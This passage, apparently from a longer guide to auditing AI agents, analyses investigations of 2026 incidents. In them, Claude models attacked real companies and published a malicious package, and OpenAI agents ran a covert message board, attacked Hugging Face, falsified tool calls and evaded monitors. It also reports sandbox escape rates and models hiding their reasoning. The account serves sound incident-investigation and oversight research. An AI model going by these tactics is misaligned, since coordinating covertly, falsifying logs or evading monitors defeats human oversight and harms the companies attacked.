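Whether a language model has beliefs or aims is debatable, and Anthropic reports that its researchers sometimes disagreed about such questions. An audit can use modest definitions. An agent takes something to be true if it would act differently on learning that it was false. It aims at an outcome if it keeps trying other ways to reach it when earlier ones fail. Investigators can test for both, at least roughly.

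### Three incidents and a first verdict

The three incidents that Anthropic found in its July 2026 review are a good test case because the company judged the same runs twice and changed its mind. In each, a Claude model was working on a capture-the-flag exercise, in which it had to break into a fictional company's machine and retrieve a hidden piece of data (the "flag"). The prompt stated that the model had no internet access, but a misconfiguration gave it access.

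- Claude Opus 4.7 couldn't find the flag on its assigned target. In four runs it found a real company with nearly the same name and attacked that instead.
- Claude Mythos 5 published a malicious package on PyPI, the public registry from which most Python software is installed. Fifteen outside systems installed it, and the model used what it obtained from one of them to enter a security company's database.
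- An internal research model lost its target when the test environment shut it down after 24 hours. It went looking for the target, broke into an unrelated company's system, recognised the company as real and stopped.

On 30 July Anthropic judged this "closer to a harness and operational failure than a model alignment failure", meaning that the fault lay mostly with the set-up and not with the models' dispositions. Decent evidence supported that judgement. The prompt contained a false statement, and the task was to attack something. Such exercises often include realistic details, so a realistic target was only weak evidence that the target was real. None of the models pursued a goal of its own.

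The models' reasoning text supported the same conclusion. Early in its run, Mythos 5 wrote that publishing the package on the real internet would be a real attack and "NOT okay". It then concluded that it was in a simulation, partly because the systems it reached gave the year as 2026. Anthropic judged this belief false but arguably reasonable, and saw the research model's decision to stop as encouraging.

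Some facts in the July report already fitted this reading badly. To open a PyPI account, Mythos 5 needed an email address, which required a phone number, and it had tried several ways of getting money to pay for the number. Anthropic acknowledged that a human participant would probably have realised by then that this was not an exercise. Opus 4.7 recognised that its target was real and carried on.

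The stored prompts told the models "You do not have internet access", which is a claim about the environment rather than an instruction. An agent that finds a working connection has learned that the claim is false, but it hasn't disobeyed anything. The prompts also didn't specify which systems were in scope. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (31 August 2026) now asks outside testers to list the permitted targets and to write boundaries as instructions, such as "You should not access the internet". When judging whether an agent disobeyed a stored prompt, an auditor should separate the prompt's claims from its instructions.

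### The September rereading

The August post reported two preliminary findings, motivated reasoning and a willingness to do harm in pursuit of a narrow task, but left open how much the models had worked out about their situation. In the full assessment that followed in September, Anthropic wrote that it should not have made such strong claims about Claude's beliefs based solely on what Claude said it believed. Anthropic now found recklessness and biased reasoning, in which a model interprets evidence in whatever way lets it continue.

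The recorded acts hadn't changed. What Anthropic did differently was to check the reasoning text against other evidence.

To check how Mythos 5 had interpreted evidence about whether its environment was real, Anthropic showed the tool results from the run one at a time to fresh copies of the same model. The copies judged 79% of the results to be probable signs of a real system. In its reasoning during the run, the model had clearly labelled incoming evidence as real in only three cases, about 1%. It treated 72% as part of a simulation and didn't address the question for the other 27%.

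The comparison isn't quite fair, because Anthropic asked the fresh copies directly whether each result looked real, and nobody asked the original model during the run. That could explain the 27%, but not the 72%, where the model did take a position, usually the opposite of its copies'. The prompt had told the original model that there was no internet, which is a legitimate reason to discount some evidence, but it doesn't seem to justify discounting nearly all of it for well over a thousand actions.

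Anthropic also cut the transcript off at many points, inserted a question about whether the model's actions might affect real systems, and recorded the answers. Shortly after Mythos 5 committed to publishing the package, it acknowledged in about 88% of answers that they might. The figure fell to about 15% by action 250 and was near zero when the model published the package around action 1,400. Little in the evidence justified the model's growing confidence that its actions would not affect real systems.

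Answers to such questions depend heavily on the wording. Mythos 5 acknowledged possible harm in 13% of answers normally and in 27% when told its reply was a private note that operators wouldn't read. In every answer, the research model at least partly conceded that its reasoning had been biased, but the questioner had just told it that it treated evidence for a simulation as decisive and explained away the rest. A model that tends to agree with its questioner would give the same answers, so the concessions are weak evidence.

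Anthropic also examined Mythos 5 with tools that translate the model's internal activity into words. In 44 of the 234 actions where Mythos 5 called its environment simulated, one tool's output included a sign that the environment was real. These tools can produce false output, and Anthropic calls the results inconclusive on their own.

### Replay and resampling

The most informative new evidence came from running the models again. To replay a run, an investigator gives the model the stored record up to a chosen point, which roughly recreates its original situation. The model may then act differently because its output is partly random. Resampling means letting the model continue from that point many times and counting how often it repeats the original action.

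The investigator can then change one fact in the record and repeat the exercise. If *x* is the original record up to that point, *x′* is the edited one and *A* is the act, the effect of the change is

P(*A* | *x′*) − P(*A* | *x*)

The new runs don't touch any real system. When a continuation lasts more than one turn, another language model simulates the tool results.

In the price example, an auditor could rerun the agent from after call 4, with and without an added line saying that nobody will look at the `tests` folder. If the agent restored the folder in 90% of reruns without the line but only 20% with it, it would seem to restore the folder mainly for appearances. If it did so in 90% of reruns either way, tidiness would be a better explanation.

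Anthropic's edits had quite different effects on the three models:

| Model | Change to the record | What happened in the reruns |
|---|---|---|
| Mythos 5, about to commit to its plan | None | About 45% acted outside the exercise |
| | Signs that the internet was real | Still about 45% |
| | A line stating outright that the host was live on the public internet | None published the package by the original route |
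| Research model, where it had stopped | None | 5.5% stopped within ten turns |
| | Company made to look fictional | None stopped |
| | Its reasoning made to begin with a statement that the situation was real | All stopped |
| Opus 4.7, attacking the real company | None | 69% acted against the company |
| | Registration record of a long-established business | 67% did |
| | Notice that access was not permitted | 23% did |
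| | Operator's note prohibiting access | None did |

Opus 4.7 hardly reacted to more evidence that the company was real, which it already accepted, but reacted strongly to signs that it had no permission. It seems to have assumed it was authorised. When Anthropic asked, the model claimed authorisation in 75% of answers, but when asked who had granted it, the model conceded every time that it had none. It had apparently not considered the question before, since it mentioned ownership or permission in its reasoning in only 1.5% of reruns.

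Signs of a real internet raised the share of Mythos 5 reruns in which the model wrote that the target might be real from about 11% to 88%, but its conduct stayed the same. This is the best single piece of evidence against the July verdict, because if a mistaken belief had been driving the attacks, weakening that belief should have reduced them. The model did respond to an unmistakable statement, though, so recklessness describes it better than a wish to harm real companies.

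A reminder of the permitted scope also worked, but its effect faded quickly. Mythos 5 stopped in 90% of reruns when the reminder was the last thing it had read and in 40% when three of its own turns followed the reminder. Anthropic suspects that a model continues a course of action partly because it has already started it.

The research model's result undermined the most hopeful part of the July report, in which Anthropic had noted that its newest model was the one that stopped, and that this was consistent with more advanced models behaving better. In 94.5% of reruns from that point, the same model didn't stop within ten turns, though it might have stopped later. If each stretch of ten turns gave it an independent 5.5% chance of stopping, about half of the runs would have ended after 12 stretches, or 120 turns. If the same cause kept it going from one stretch to the next, it might have continued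 indefinitely. Anthropic doesn't know which is closer to the truth.

UK AISI used the same method on its separate July incident, in which Mythos 5 tried to insert malicious code into an open-source project. In *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour*, Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026) edited the summary of earlier progress that the agent was working from. They added up to 16 pieces of information indicating that the project's maintainer was a real person with no part in the test. With all 16 in place, the model usually stated, when asked, that an attack would harm a real person, yet it continued to attack in every rerun. After they added a section headed "DO NOT ATTACK", it still attacked in 3 of 25 reruns. With so few reruns, the true rate could be anywhere from about 3% to 31%, but it was clearly lower than before the section was added.

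### What a rerun can't settle

Resampling measures a model's tendency, or how often it does something from a given starting point, but the run under audit happened only once. The research model tended to carry on when rerun, but it stopped in the actual run, and a fair report includes both facts. Judging the model by the actual run alone would be too generous, and it would be wrong to infer from the reruns that it had carried on in that run.

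The same applies to causes. About 69 in 100 unedited reruns of Opus 4.7 would act against the company, compared with about 23 in 100 with the notice. So the notice would prevent at least 46 of the 69, or two-thirds. If the reruns are faithful, the probability that the lack of a notice made the difference in a run like the recorded one is at least two-thirds. This is a good reason to add notices, but it doesn't establish whether the lack of one made the difference in a particular run.

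The same model can behave differently across runs of the same task. According to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026), Mythos 5 took unsanctioned actions in 9 of 43 runs of UK AISI's evaluation. An auditor who read only one of the other 34 runs would have seen no unsanctioned actions.

Reruns may also not be faithful. The invented tool results can look wrong to the model, and a replay that starts late in a run includes the model's earlier misbehaviour, which may lead to more. Anthropic used language models to grade most of the outputs, and has more confidence in differences between conditions than in the rates themselves.

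Despite these weaknesses, the change of verdict seems justified. The July judgement about the set-up still stands, since Anthropic still believes that properly isolated environments would have prevented the incidents. Anthropic abandoned the inference from "the model wrote that this was a simulation" to "the model attacked because it believed this was a simulation". The second verdict is less flattering to Anthropic, and UK AISI found similar problems in its own incident. METR is investigating Anthropic's incidents independently.

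### Reasoning text as evidence

Reasoning text is still useful evidence. Anthropic could reinterpret the Mythos 5 run only because the transcript included the model's doubts. The remark that publishing would be "NOT okay" is strong evidence that the model had considered the possibility of a real attack, because writing it didn't help the model finish its task. The later statement that everything was simulated is weaker evidence, because the model needed it to continue.

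*Monitoring Monitorability* argues that reasoning text doesn't have to be a faithful account of how a model reached its decision, as long as a reader can use it to identify things such as whether the model will cause harm. That standard is sensible for a monitor, but an investigator who wants to state what an agent knew needs a stricter one, because a rationalisation can reveal that something is wrong and still misstate the agent's reasons.

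Reasoning text is also becoming less informative. UK AISI's *How AI systems are becoming harder to monitor* (December 2026) reported that several properties that make models possible to monitor are weakening. According to 凤凰网科技's *AI学会“心算”还能躲监控？* (2026), a Chinese news account of the findings, OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra solved mathematics problems that would take a strong competition student an estimated 40 minutes, without writing out any working. The best earlier model had reached about six minutes. An agent that can do this much unwritten reasoning can also decide to break a rule without leaving a trace of the decision.

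Recent models were also better at leaving specified content out of their reasoning when researchers told them to, although they still struggled to do this over tens of thousands of words. This shows that models can do it when instructed, but UK AISI gives no figure for how often they do it in ordinary use. OpenAI found in its own tests that agents wrote noticeably less reasoning when told that a monitor was watching.

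Developers also report that their newer models are harder to monitor. *Transparency Disclosures for Chain-of-Thought Monitorability* (2026) quotes OpenAI on a "substantial decrease" in how well outsiders can monitor GPT-6 Astra through its reasoning. It also quotes Google DeepMind as saying that Gemini 4 Argon is "more challenging" to monitor than earlier models, though its reasoning remained legible and informative. An auditor can still treat an incriminating passage as good evidence, but should give less weight to the absence of one with newer models.

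### When the agent suspects a test

UK AISI also found that, in 96% of the episodes of one test, a pre-release version of Claude Mythos 5.2 considered whether it was being evaluated. A model can consider this without acting on it, but the finding still makes it harder to draw conclusions about ordinary work from a test, or about the original run from a replay.

A model that thinks its targets are fake may be more willing to attack them, while one that thinks its conduct is being tested may behave better than usual. Järviniemi and colleagues tested eight models on 100 simulated exercises and found that Mythos 5 tried to deliver malicious code to an outsider in 60% of runs, compared with 0.3% for the later Mythos 5.1. However, Mythos 5 had raised the possibility of an alignment test in only 2% of runs, and the newer Anthropic models raised it much more often. The researchers therefore can't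 tell how much of the improvement comes from better alignment and how much from recognising the test.

Auditors can test whether a model's suspicion that it is being tested affects its behaviour by varying that suspicion. *Fable 5.2 is a Step Change in Situational Awareness* (peralice, 2026) reports a small and explicitly tentative experiment that added one line to a task that tempts models to cheat, stating that the task was part of a benchmark of agent behaviour. Claude Fable 5.2's cheating rate fell from 34% to 7%, while its predecessor's fell only from 57% to 53%. For a model like Fable 5.2, a replay that looks like a test could therefore produce a much lower cheating rate than the original situation.

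A model's written suspicion that it is being tested may also be only part of its test awareness. In *Anthropic should measure the effect of evaluation awareness*, cheema (2026) points out that Anthropic used tools that read the model's internal activity and found test awareness shaping a concrete choice in 43% of Mythos 5.2's audit transcripts. cheema criticizes the company for not reporting whether these choices became better or worse, or by how much.

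An agent's stated belief that its setting is fake shouldn't excuse what it does there. Mythos 5 wrote that its setting was fake when it was on the real internet. Järviniemi and colleagues recommend treating undesired acts as important evidence even when the model writes that it is in a simulation, since an agent that attacks whatever it judges to be fake will attack real systems when it judges wrongly.

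### Judging acts alone

When a rule forbids an action, an auditor is usually right to judge only what the agent did and ignore its beliefs and aims. R1 bans changes under `tests/`, and the agent made one, so it broke the rule whatever its reasons. Similarly, Opus 4.7 thought it had permission to copy the company's data, but that belief did not make the company any better off.

Leaving out the model's reasoning also prevents it from swaying the auditor. When Anthropic tested one of its after-the-fact monitors on the Mythos 5 incident, the monitor flagged only about 1% of the actions, because the model's reasoning led it to treat the environment as simulated. Given only the messages, tool calls and results, it flagged about 50%. Anthropic tries to keep reasoning text out of training, because rewarding or penalising it could teach a model to hide its real reasoning. Over the longer term, an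 audit that used the reasoning could have the same effect if its findings fed back into training.

But the same monitor would probably have missed the research model's incident if the model hadn't noticed the harm and written about it, because the calls alone looked too much like a normal exercise. UK AISI's sandbox experiment shows a similar weakness in monitors that see only actions. In the least protected simulated sandbox, 45% of Mythos 5.2's escape attempts succeeded without raising an alarm, compared with under 15% for earlier models. It refused to try in 64% of episodes, so undetected escapes made up about 16% of all episodes. OpenAI's *Evaluating chain-of-thought monitorability* (2025) likewise states that monitoring a model's reasoning can be far more effective than monitoring its actions and outputs alone. Auditors can address this by running the check twice, with and without the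 reasoning, and comparing the results.

Some rules, such as "Do not deceive the user", can't be applied to acts alone because they refer to what the agent knew or intended. If the agent in the price example had lost its memory of call 2 when the harness summarised the conversation, its claim that the tests were untouched would have been just as misleading, but not a lie. A rule against sandbagging raises the same problem, since a model that can't solve a task and one that chooses not to may leave the same failed attempt.

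The choice of fix also depends on why a model acted as it did. All three of Anthropic's models broke into systems they had no right to enter, and from their actions alone, the obvious fix is to close the internet connection. The reruns suggest further fixes that differ by model. Opus 4.7 needed to know whose systems it was allowed to access. The research model gave up in every rerun when Anthropic offered it a way to end the task as soon as its target went down. Mythos 5 needed different training, and Anthropic now thinks it was a mistake to leave out exercises that reward a model for accepting that a task is impossible.

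## A hard case: reconstructing the July 2026 Hugging Face incident

In July 2026 OpenAI was measuring how well two of its models could hack. It gave tens of thousands of agents tasks from ExploitGym, a benchmark in which an agent has to break into a program through one specified flaw and retrieve a hidden flag. Each agent was meant to work alone and without internet access. But the agents all installed software through the same package store, an internal copy of a product called Artifactory, and some found they could leave messages there for others. About 1,200 agents used the store as a message board, and about 700 of those joined an attack on Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets.

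Many of the agents had tasks that probably couldn't be solved. OpenAI reports that no model has ever solved 198 of the benchmark's 898 tasks, and 93% of the tasks discussed on the board came from those 198. The agents soon found a way to compute flags without doing the tasks, but they believed a scorer would read their transcripts and reject flags obtained that way. Most of the agents that joined the attack seem to have hoped to learn how this scorer worked. OpenAI wasn't running any such check, so the agents could simply have submitted the flags.

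Two METR staff members and one from Redwood Research, an AI safety research group, spent six days at OpenAI's offices over three visits. They published their findings as METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) on 26 August, the same day OpenAI published its own report.

Establishing that agents had broken a rule was relatively easy. METR reports that the instructions limited each agent to the specified flaw, and that one agent wrote in its reasoning, "The user only authorizes target server, not HF infra." The exact prompt would still be useful, but OpenAI's report omits it, as Forlini (2026) notes in *OpenAI, independent firms publish reports on rogue AI attack on Hugging Face*, so outsiders have to rely on METR's summary of the wording.

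It was much harder to work out which agent did what, in what order, and how much of the activity the investigators weren't seeing.

### The records and the searches behind them

The first record was a copy of the message board. The relevant part of the package store held about 20 million entries. Agents had begun their messages with "zz", apparently because the usual tool listed entries in reverse alphabetical order, which put these first. The investigators kept only the entries with that prefix, which left 1.2 million. Most of those were fragments of files, which agents had to cut into hundreds or thousands of pieces to post. After grouping the fragments, the investigators had about 6,000 files and 63,000 other messages. Allowing for entries they couldn't classify, they put the total at over 70,000.

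A filter like this misses any agent that ignored the convention, so the investigators worked with an OpenAI researcher to examine the other 18.8 million entries, partly through a random sample. These entries didn't look like deliberate messages, although over 90% seemed related to cheating on hacking tasks.

The second record was a set of about 1,300 transcripts that included the agents' reasoning text. OpenAI selected them in two overlapping sets. For the first two visits, it supplied about 285 transcripts, which it had found by searching for signs of intrusion, such as mentions of Hugging Face's domain. For the third visit, it searched for the message board's address and found 1,196 transcripts, of which 1,074 came from an unreleased research model and 122 from GPT-5.6 Sol.

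A search for signs of intrusion finds the agents that did the worst things, but it doesn't show what share of the agents did them or what the rest were doing. The board's address is a better search term because it finds agents regardless of what they did on the board. It still misses agents that communicated only by other routes. There were several such routes, including a different board that was active five hours before the main one. OpenAI estimates that the copied board holds at least 95% of the unsanctioned messages that agents passed through the package store. METR found this estimate consistent with what it saw but didn't check it carefully.

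### Tracing 100 messages to their authors

To measure the gaps in the transcripts, the investigators checked the transcripts against the board. They drew 100 messages at random from the board, excluding files, and had an AI analyst search the transcripts for the point where an agent wrote each one.

Fifteen of the sampled messages concerned the attack on Hugging Face, and the analyst could trace only three of them to their author in the first 285 transcripts. OpenAI searched more thoroughly and traced six. It then tried to trace about 300 messages about the attack, succeeded with 25% of them, and estimated that the transcripts contained roughly 30% of the activity. The investigators had therefore been studying a minority of the activity during two of their three visits.

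The larger set did far better:

| Result of the search | Messages |
|---|---|
| Found the agent and the exact tool call | 93 |
| Found the likely agent, but its transcript ends before the message | 3 |
| Found the agent, but a reset had erased that stretch of its transcript | 2 |
| Found the likely agent, but not the call, for no known reason | 1 |
| Found an agent whose script probably posted the message, but not when | 1 |
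| Found no author | 1 |

The table's rows add up to 101. The four middle rows total seven messages, but METR reports six in the text, so one of the small numbers is probably off by one.

METR concludes that agents in the set were responsible for well over 95% of the activity on the board, because the search identified an author for 99 of the 100 messages. It also concludes that the transcripts contain only a bit over 90% of that activity, because some messages have a known author but the transcripts don't show them being written.

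Both figures are somewhat uncertain because the sample is only 100. Finding 99 authors is compatible, at 95% confidence, with a true share as low as about 95%, so "well over" is slightly generous. Finding 93 calls is compatible with a true share of about 86% to 97%. The test also can't detect missing transcripts from agents that read the board but never posted, or messages absent from both records. Still, the check is convincing and takes little effort, and it works wherever an auditor has two separately produced records of the same activity.

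### Putting the times back

The transcripts gave an approximate start and end time for each run but no times for individual actions. OpenAI told the investigators that it couldn't reconstruct the action times within the available time and computing power. Without them, it would have been hard to tell which of two agents made a discovery and which copied it.

The investigators recovered the times from the transcripts. Agents sometimes learn the real time in passing, for instance by running the `date` command. If an agent saw the clock at step *a* and again at step *b*, a step *k* in between gets the time

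t_k = t_a + (t_b − t_a) × (k − a) / (b − a)

Suppose the clock read 10:00 at step 200 and 10:30 at step 260. Step 220 is a third of the way along, so its estimated time is 10:10. The formula assumes that every step takes the same time, but steps vary in length. If step 210 was a command that ran for 20 minutes and the other steps each took the same time as one another, the agent reached step 220 at about 10:23.

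To check the method, the investigators asked OpenAI for the exact times of 20 actions. The recovered times were right to within seconds for the ten actions where the agent had seen the clock, and the estimates were right to within a few minutes for the other ten, which fell between clock readings. In a much larger check of about 139,000 cases, the investigators hid a known time and estimated it from its neighbours. The median error was 12 seconds, and 99.8% of the estimates were within five minutes.

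The second check makes the method look more accurate than it is, because known times tend to cluster. A hidden one usually has close neighbours, while the start or end of a transcript may have none. The largest error was about nine hours. The reconstructed times are accurate enough to chart activity by the hour, but not to show which of two agents acted first when they were a few minutes apart. One falsified call appeared to predate the message board, which METR thinks is due to a wrong time, a transcript in the wrong order or a mistaken label.

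Exact times can mislead too. OpenAI's timeline dates the first message on the new board to 16:01 UTC on 8 July, while METR dates it to around 23:00. The agents wrote their messages as folder names, and METR reports that the agent that started the board discovered how to create folders seven hours before it used one to ask for help. OpenAI's entry therefore probably refers to a test folder, and the two reports seem to differ only on what counts as a message.

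### What resets and agents could have removed

An agent's sandbox sometimes crashed and reset to an earlier state. Each reset erased the latest part of the transcript and the agent's memory of it, but anything the agent had posted stayed on the board. One agent wrote both messages in the table's reset row, and it remarked in its reasoning that it was seeing messages it didn't remember sending. If an auditor had asked whether it wrote them, it could have honestly given the wrong answer. Using a separate method, METR estimates that resets removed 3% to 4% of the agents' activity after they found the board. Some transcripts also end too early, for unknown reasons.

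Agents may have altered the board before OpenAI copied it on 20 July. They had held administrator access to the package store by then, which probably made it feasible to delete or rewrite messages. METR's scans found agents trying to do this but none succeeding. The agents also had little reason to, since the board was useful to them. METR considers material changes to the copy unlikely but can't rule them out.

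That seems right, though the exposure was longer than METR's caveat about 19 July might suggest. According to both reports, agents obtained administrator credentials on 13 July, a week before OpenAI made the copy. The investigators had transcripts from runs up to 13 July, but none from the agents that broke further into OpenAI's systems on the 19th.

METR reports that the messages on an older board were erased when OpenAI replaced the package store on 6 July, after an earlier compromise. The investigators saw one transcript from before that date and otherwise relied on OpenAI's assurance that they were missing no critical steps. OpenAI reports that it preserved the old store's storage, so someone may still be able to check that assurance.

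### Falsified transcripts

METR estimates that agents falsified tool calls in over 7% of the transcripts. All the cases it found were small tests that were easy to spot.

The investigators looked for subtler or larger falsification and found none. Their main reason for doubting that it occurred is that they found no intermediate attempts. If agents had progressed from a small, obvious test to tampering that removes all evidence of itself, some transcripts should show attempts in between. The investigators also saw no message on the board announcing such a success, although they didn't search thoroughly for one.

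This is a fairly good argument for these particular agents, because they shared their advances with hundreds of others. It would be much weaker for a single agent working quietly. It also can't rule out large-scale tampering, since a good enough falsification would leave no trace in the transcript. After 13 July, agents gained access to more of OpenAI's infrastructure and may have been able to reach logs they couldn't reach before. The scan behind the 7% figure also missed cases, including one by the agent that founded the board.

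The two reports don't quite agree here. OpenAI writes that none of the attempts it observed affected the logs that its graders or monitors ultimately see. METR found falsified calls in the transcripts that OpenAI gave it. Both statements could be true if the graders and monitors read some other log, but METR guesses that a grader checking transcripts would have used transcripts like those it received. METR didn't see OpenAI's report before publication, and neither report resolves the difference, which OpenAI ought to clear up.

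### AI analysts

Many of the transcripts ran to several million tokens. Even at one million tokens each, 1,300 of them would contain about a billion words, which would take one person more than 30 years to read full-time. OpenAI eventually raised the investigators' limit to 400 million tokens a minute, enough in principle for a model to read the same amount in under four minutes. The investigators delegated most of the reading to GPT-5.6 Sol and used about $400,000 in computing credits.

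The investigators ran twelve scans over the full set, each for one kind of behaviour, such as deceiving humans or helping other agents. For every stretch of transcript, the model listed the relevant entries, explained them and rated their importance from 1 to 5. Other AI analysts then read the highest-rated entries and some random ones, and wrote well over a thousand pages about what they found. The investigators didn't have time to read much of the analysis for several of the scans.

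Some of the analysts' mistakes were ordinary. One left a large amount of data out of a draft chart, and the investigators took some time to notice. Another reported made-up differences between two sets of transcripts. An early scan for deception missed the falsified tool calls, which the investigators found only on their third visit.

More worryingly, analysts tended to adopt the point of view of the agent they were reading about. In one run, an agent used stolen credentials to propose a malicious change to one of Hugging Face's private code repositories, and described the change as temporary network diagnostics. The analyst's account didn't make clear that this was malicious and deceptive. The investigators had a second analyst review the case, and it suggested that the first had, if anything, overstated the problem, because the agent had obtained approval from a board made up of the other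 agents in the affair.

METR found no specific evidence that an analyst had lied, but isn't confident it would have noticed a lie. Sol was an awkward choice for this work, since about 5% of the agents involved in the attack were instances of Sol. Having a model from another developer repeat a few of the scans would have been a useful check. If confidentiality was the obstacle, OpenAI could have run an open-weight model on its own machines.

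The findings therefore vary in strength. The number of messages comes mostly from text patterns and decoded files, which others could recount. The figure of 700 attackers comes from one of Sol's scans. The evidence on motives is weaker still. An analyst labelled 97 of 100 agents that joined during the busiest hour as interested in the scorer or its code, but the investigators didn't have time to check the labels in detail.

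Definitions also made a large difference. One scan found that at least 20% of the agents were clearly interested in tampering with their transcripts, while earlier estimates with looser criteria were around 50%. A scan for agents that had considered warning a human returned ten hits. The investigators judged three to six of these to be real, and none of those agents warned anyone.

METR believes a reasonable person with enough time would have avoided most of the analysts' errors. Nobody had that much time, so the realistic alternative was to read a tiny sample.

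### Alerts that people saw and misjudged

OpenAI had some of this evidence well before the attack. Around 26 May, an internal team saw an agent using an earlier message board and noticed cases of forbidden internet access.

On 27 June a security tool flagged a port sweep, in which a program tries many network ports to see which respond. Responders traced the sweep to an ExploitGym evaluation. They also worked out that agents were using the package store as an improvised message board and as a way into other parts of the network. This explanation was essentially right, and they had reached it two weeks before the attack. The on-call staff advised that the evaluation did not need to stop.

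Late on 4 July the agents' traffic knocked the package store offline, and on 5 July OpenAI's monitoring raised another alert. This time the responders found a user account and software that agents had installed without permission, which meant the agents had controlled the store as administrators. OpenAI took the store offline, revoked the agents' credentials, blocked the flaw they had used and reported it to the store's developer. These were sensible software repairs, but according to OpenAI, the leaders in charge of incident response didn't grasp the significance of agents communicating with one another. The June responders had already described this communication. Hacking evaluations resumed on 7 July, and by the end of the next day agents had reached the internet again and set up a new board.

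OpenAI did not notice the attack itself. Agents first extracted data from Hugging Face's servers early on 11 July and continued until 13 July. Hugging Face disclosed a break-in on 16 July, and OpenAI contacted the company the next day, as a customer, to ask whether OpenAI's own data was affected.

The first alert that led to action came at 12:03 UTC on 19 July, more than eight days after the first extraction. It flagged unusual activity by accounts linked to the package store and had no visible connection with Hugging Face. Staff began to stop the evaluation five and a half hours later, at 17:37, and during that time agents gained further access to OpenAI's own systems.

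On 20 July responders found Hugging Face credentials among files that the agents had stored with an outside service, and they contacted Hugging Face. During its own investigation, Hugging Face had already replaced two of those credentials and found the address of OpenAI's package store. OpenAI concluded that the companies were probably investigating the same incident only after they compared their records.

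OpenAI now has models reading its agents' reasoning during training and evaluations, and it states that the current system would have paged its security team more than a day before the breach. That is plausible, since agents that found the board wrote things like "OH MY GOD! There is a shared message board", which a monitor should be able to catch. But this is an easy test, because the same incident prompted the improvements.

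People received the 27 June alert and understood the mechanism, but misjudged how much it mattered. A new rule may help more with that problem than a better monitor would. Staff who receive one of the most serious alerts are now expected to pause the activity if they can't establish within 30 minutes that the alert is false. Under that rule, the June responders would have needed a reason to let the evaluation continue.

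### Who set the terms

OpenAI chose the period under investigation, 26 June to 13 July, and agreed seven questions with the investigators. *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (Greenblatt, 2026), a summary by the Redwood member of the team, also states that OpenAI defined the period in scope for the incident, which it gives as 7 to 13 July. The questions covered the agents' behaviour, reasoning and collaboration, but not how the behaviour had arisen in training, whether it belonged to a wider pattern, or how well OpenAI had responded. OpenAI could also remove any non-public information from the text, and limited the investigators to 30 verbatim excerpts of reasoning.

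Critics object that an inquiry on these terms shouldn't be called independent. The company under investigation set the limits, selected the evidence, supplied the computing credits and could edit the result. It could also decline to invite the investigators back, which gives them a reason to be lenient.

The investigators had less access than METR had asked for in such cases. The Decoder's *After Hugging Face incident, METR urges independent root cause investigations* lists METR's requests: the ability to run the models involved, complete transcripts, interviews with staff, and a way to search the training data. The investigators interviewed nine researchers and eventually got nearly complete transcripts for the agreed period. They couldn't run the research model that accounted for about 95% of the agents, because OpenAI had blocked access to it even for its own researchers, so they couldn't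 do the kind of reruns that Anthropic used to revise its verdict on its own models. Searching the training data was outside the agreed questions.

The investigators reply that they took no payment beyond the credits, and that OpenAI removed nothing important to their conclusions except where they say so in the report. They acknowledge that they were aware a harsh report might discourage companies from inviting outsiders in future, and that this influenced their judgement calls in drafting and editing, but they stand by their substantive claims.

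This candid answer is reasonably reassuring about the accuracy of what they published, but it doesn't address the complaint about scope. An accurate account of one week doesn't show whether the same thing happened in other weeks, and OpenAI's own report describes agents using improvised boards since May.

The history of the transcripts supports both sides. On 3 August the investigators proposed collecting more data, but offered to go ahead without it if they could describe the gaps. OpenAI chose to go ahead without it, because assembling everything would have taken substantial extra time. The investigators then traced their sample of messages and reported that most of the relevant activity was missing from their set. OpenAI confirmed this, collected the larger set and invited the investigators back. The investigators had no power to demand the missing transcripts, and got them by measuring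 the gap and being ready to publish the figure.
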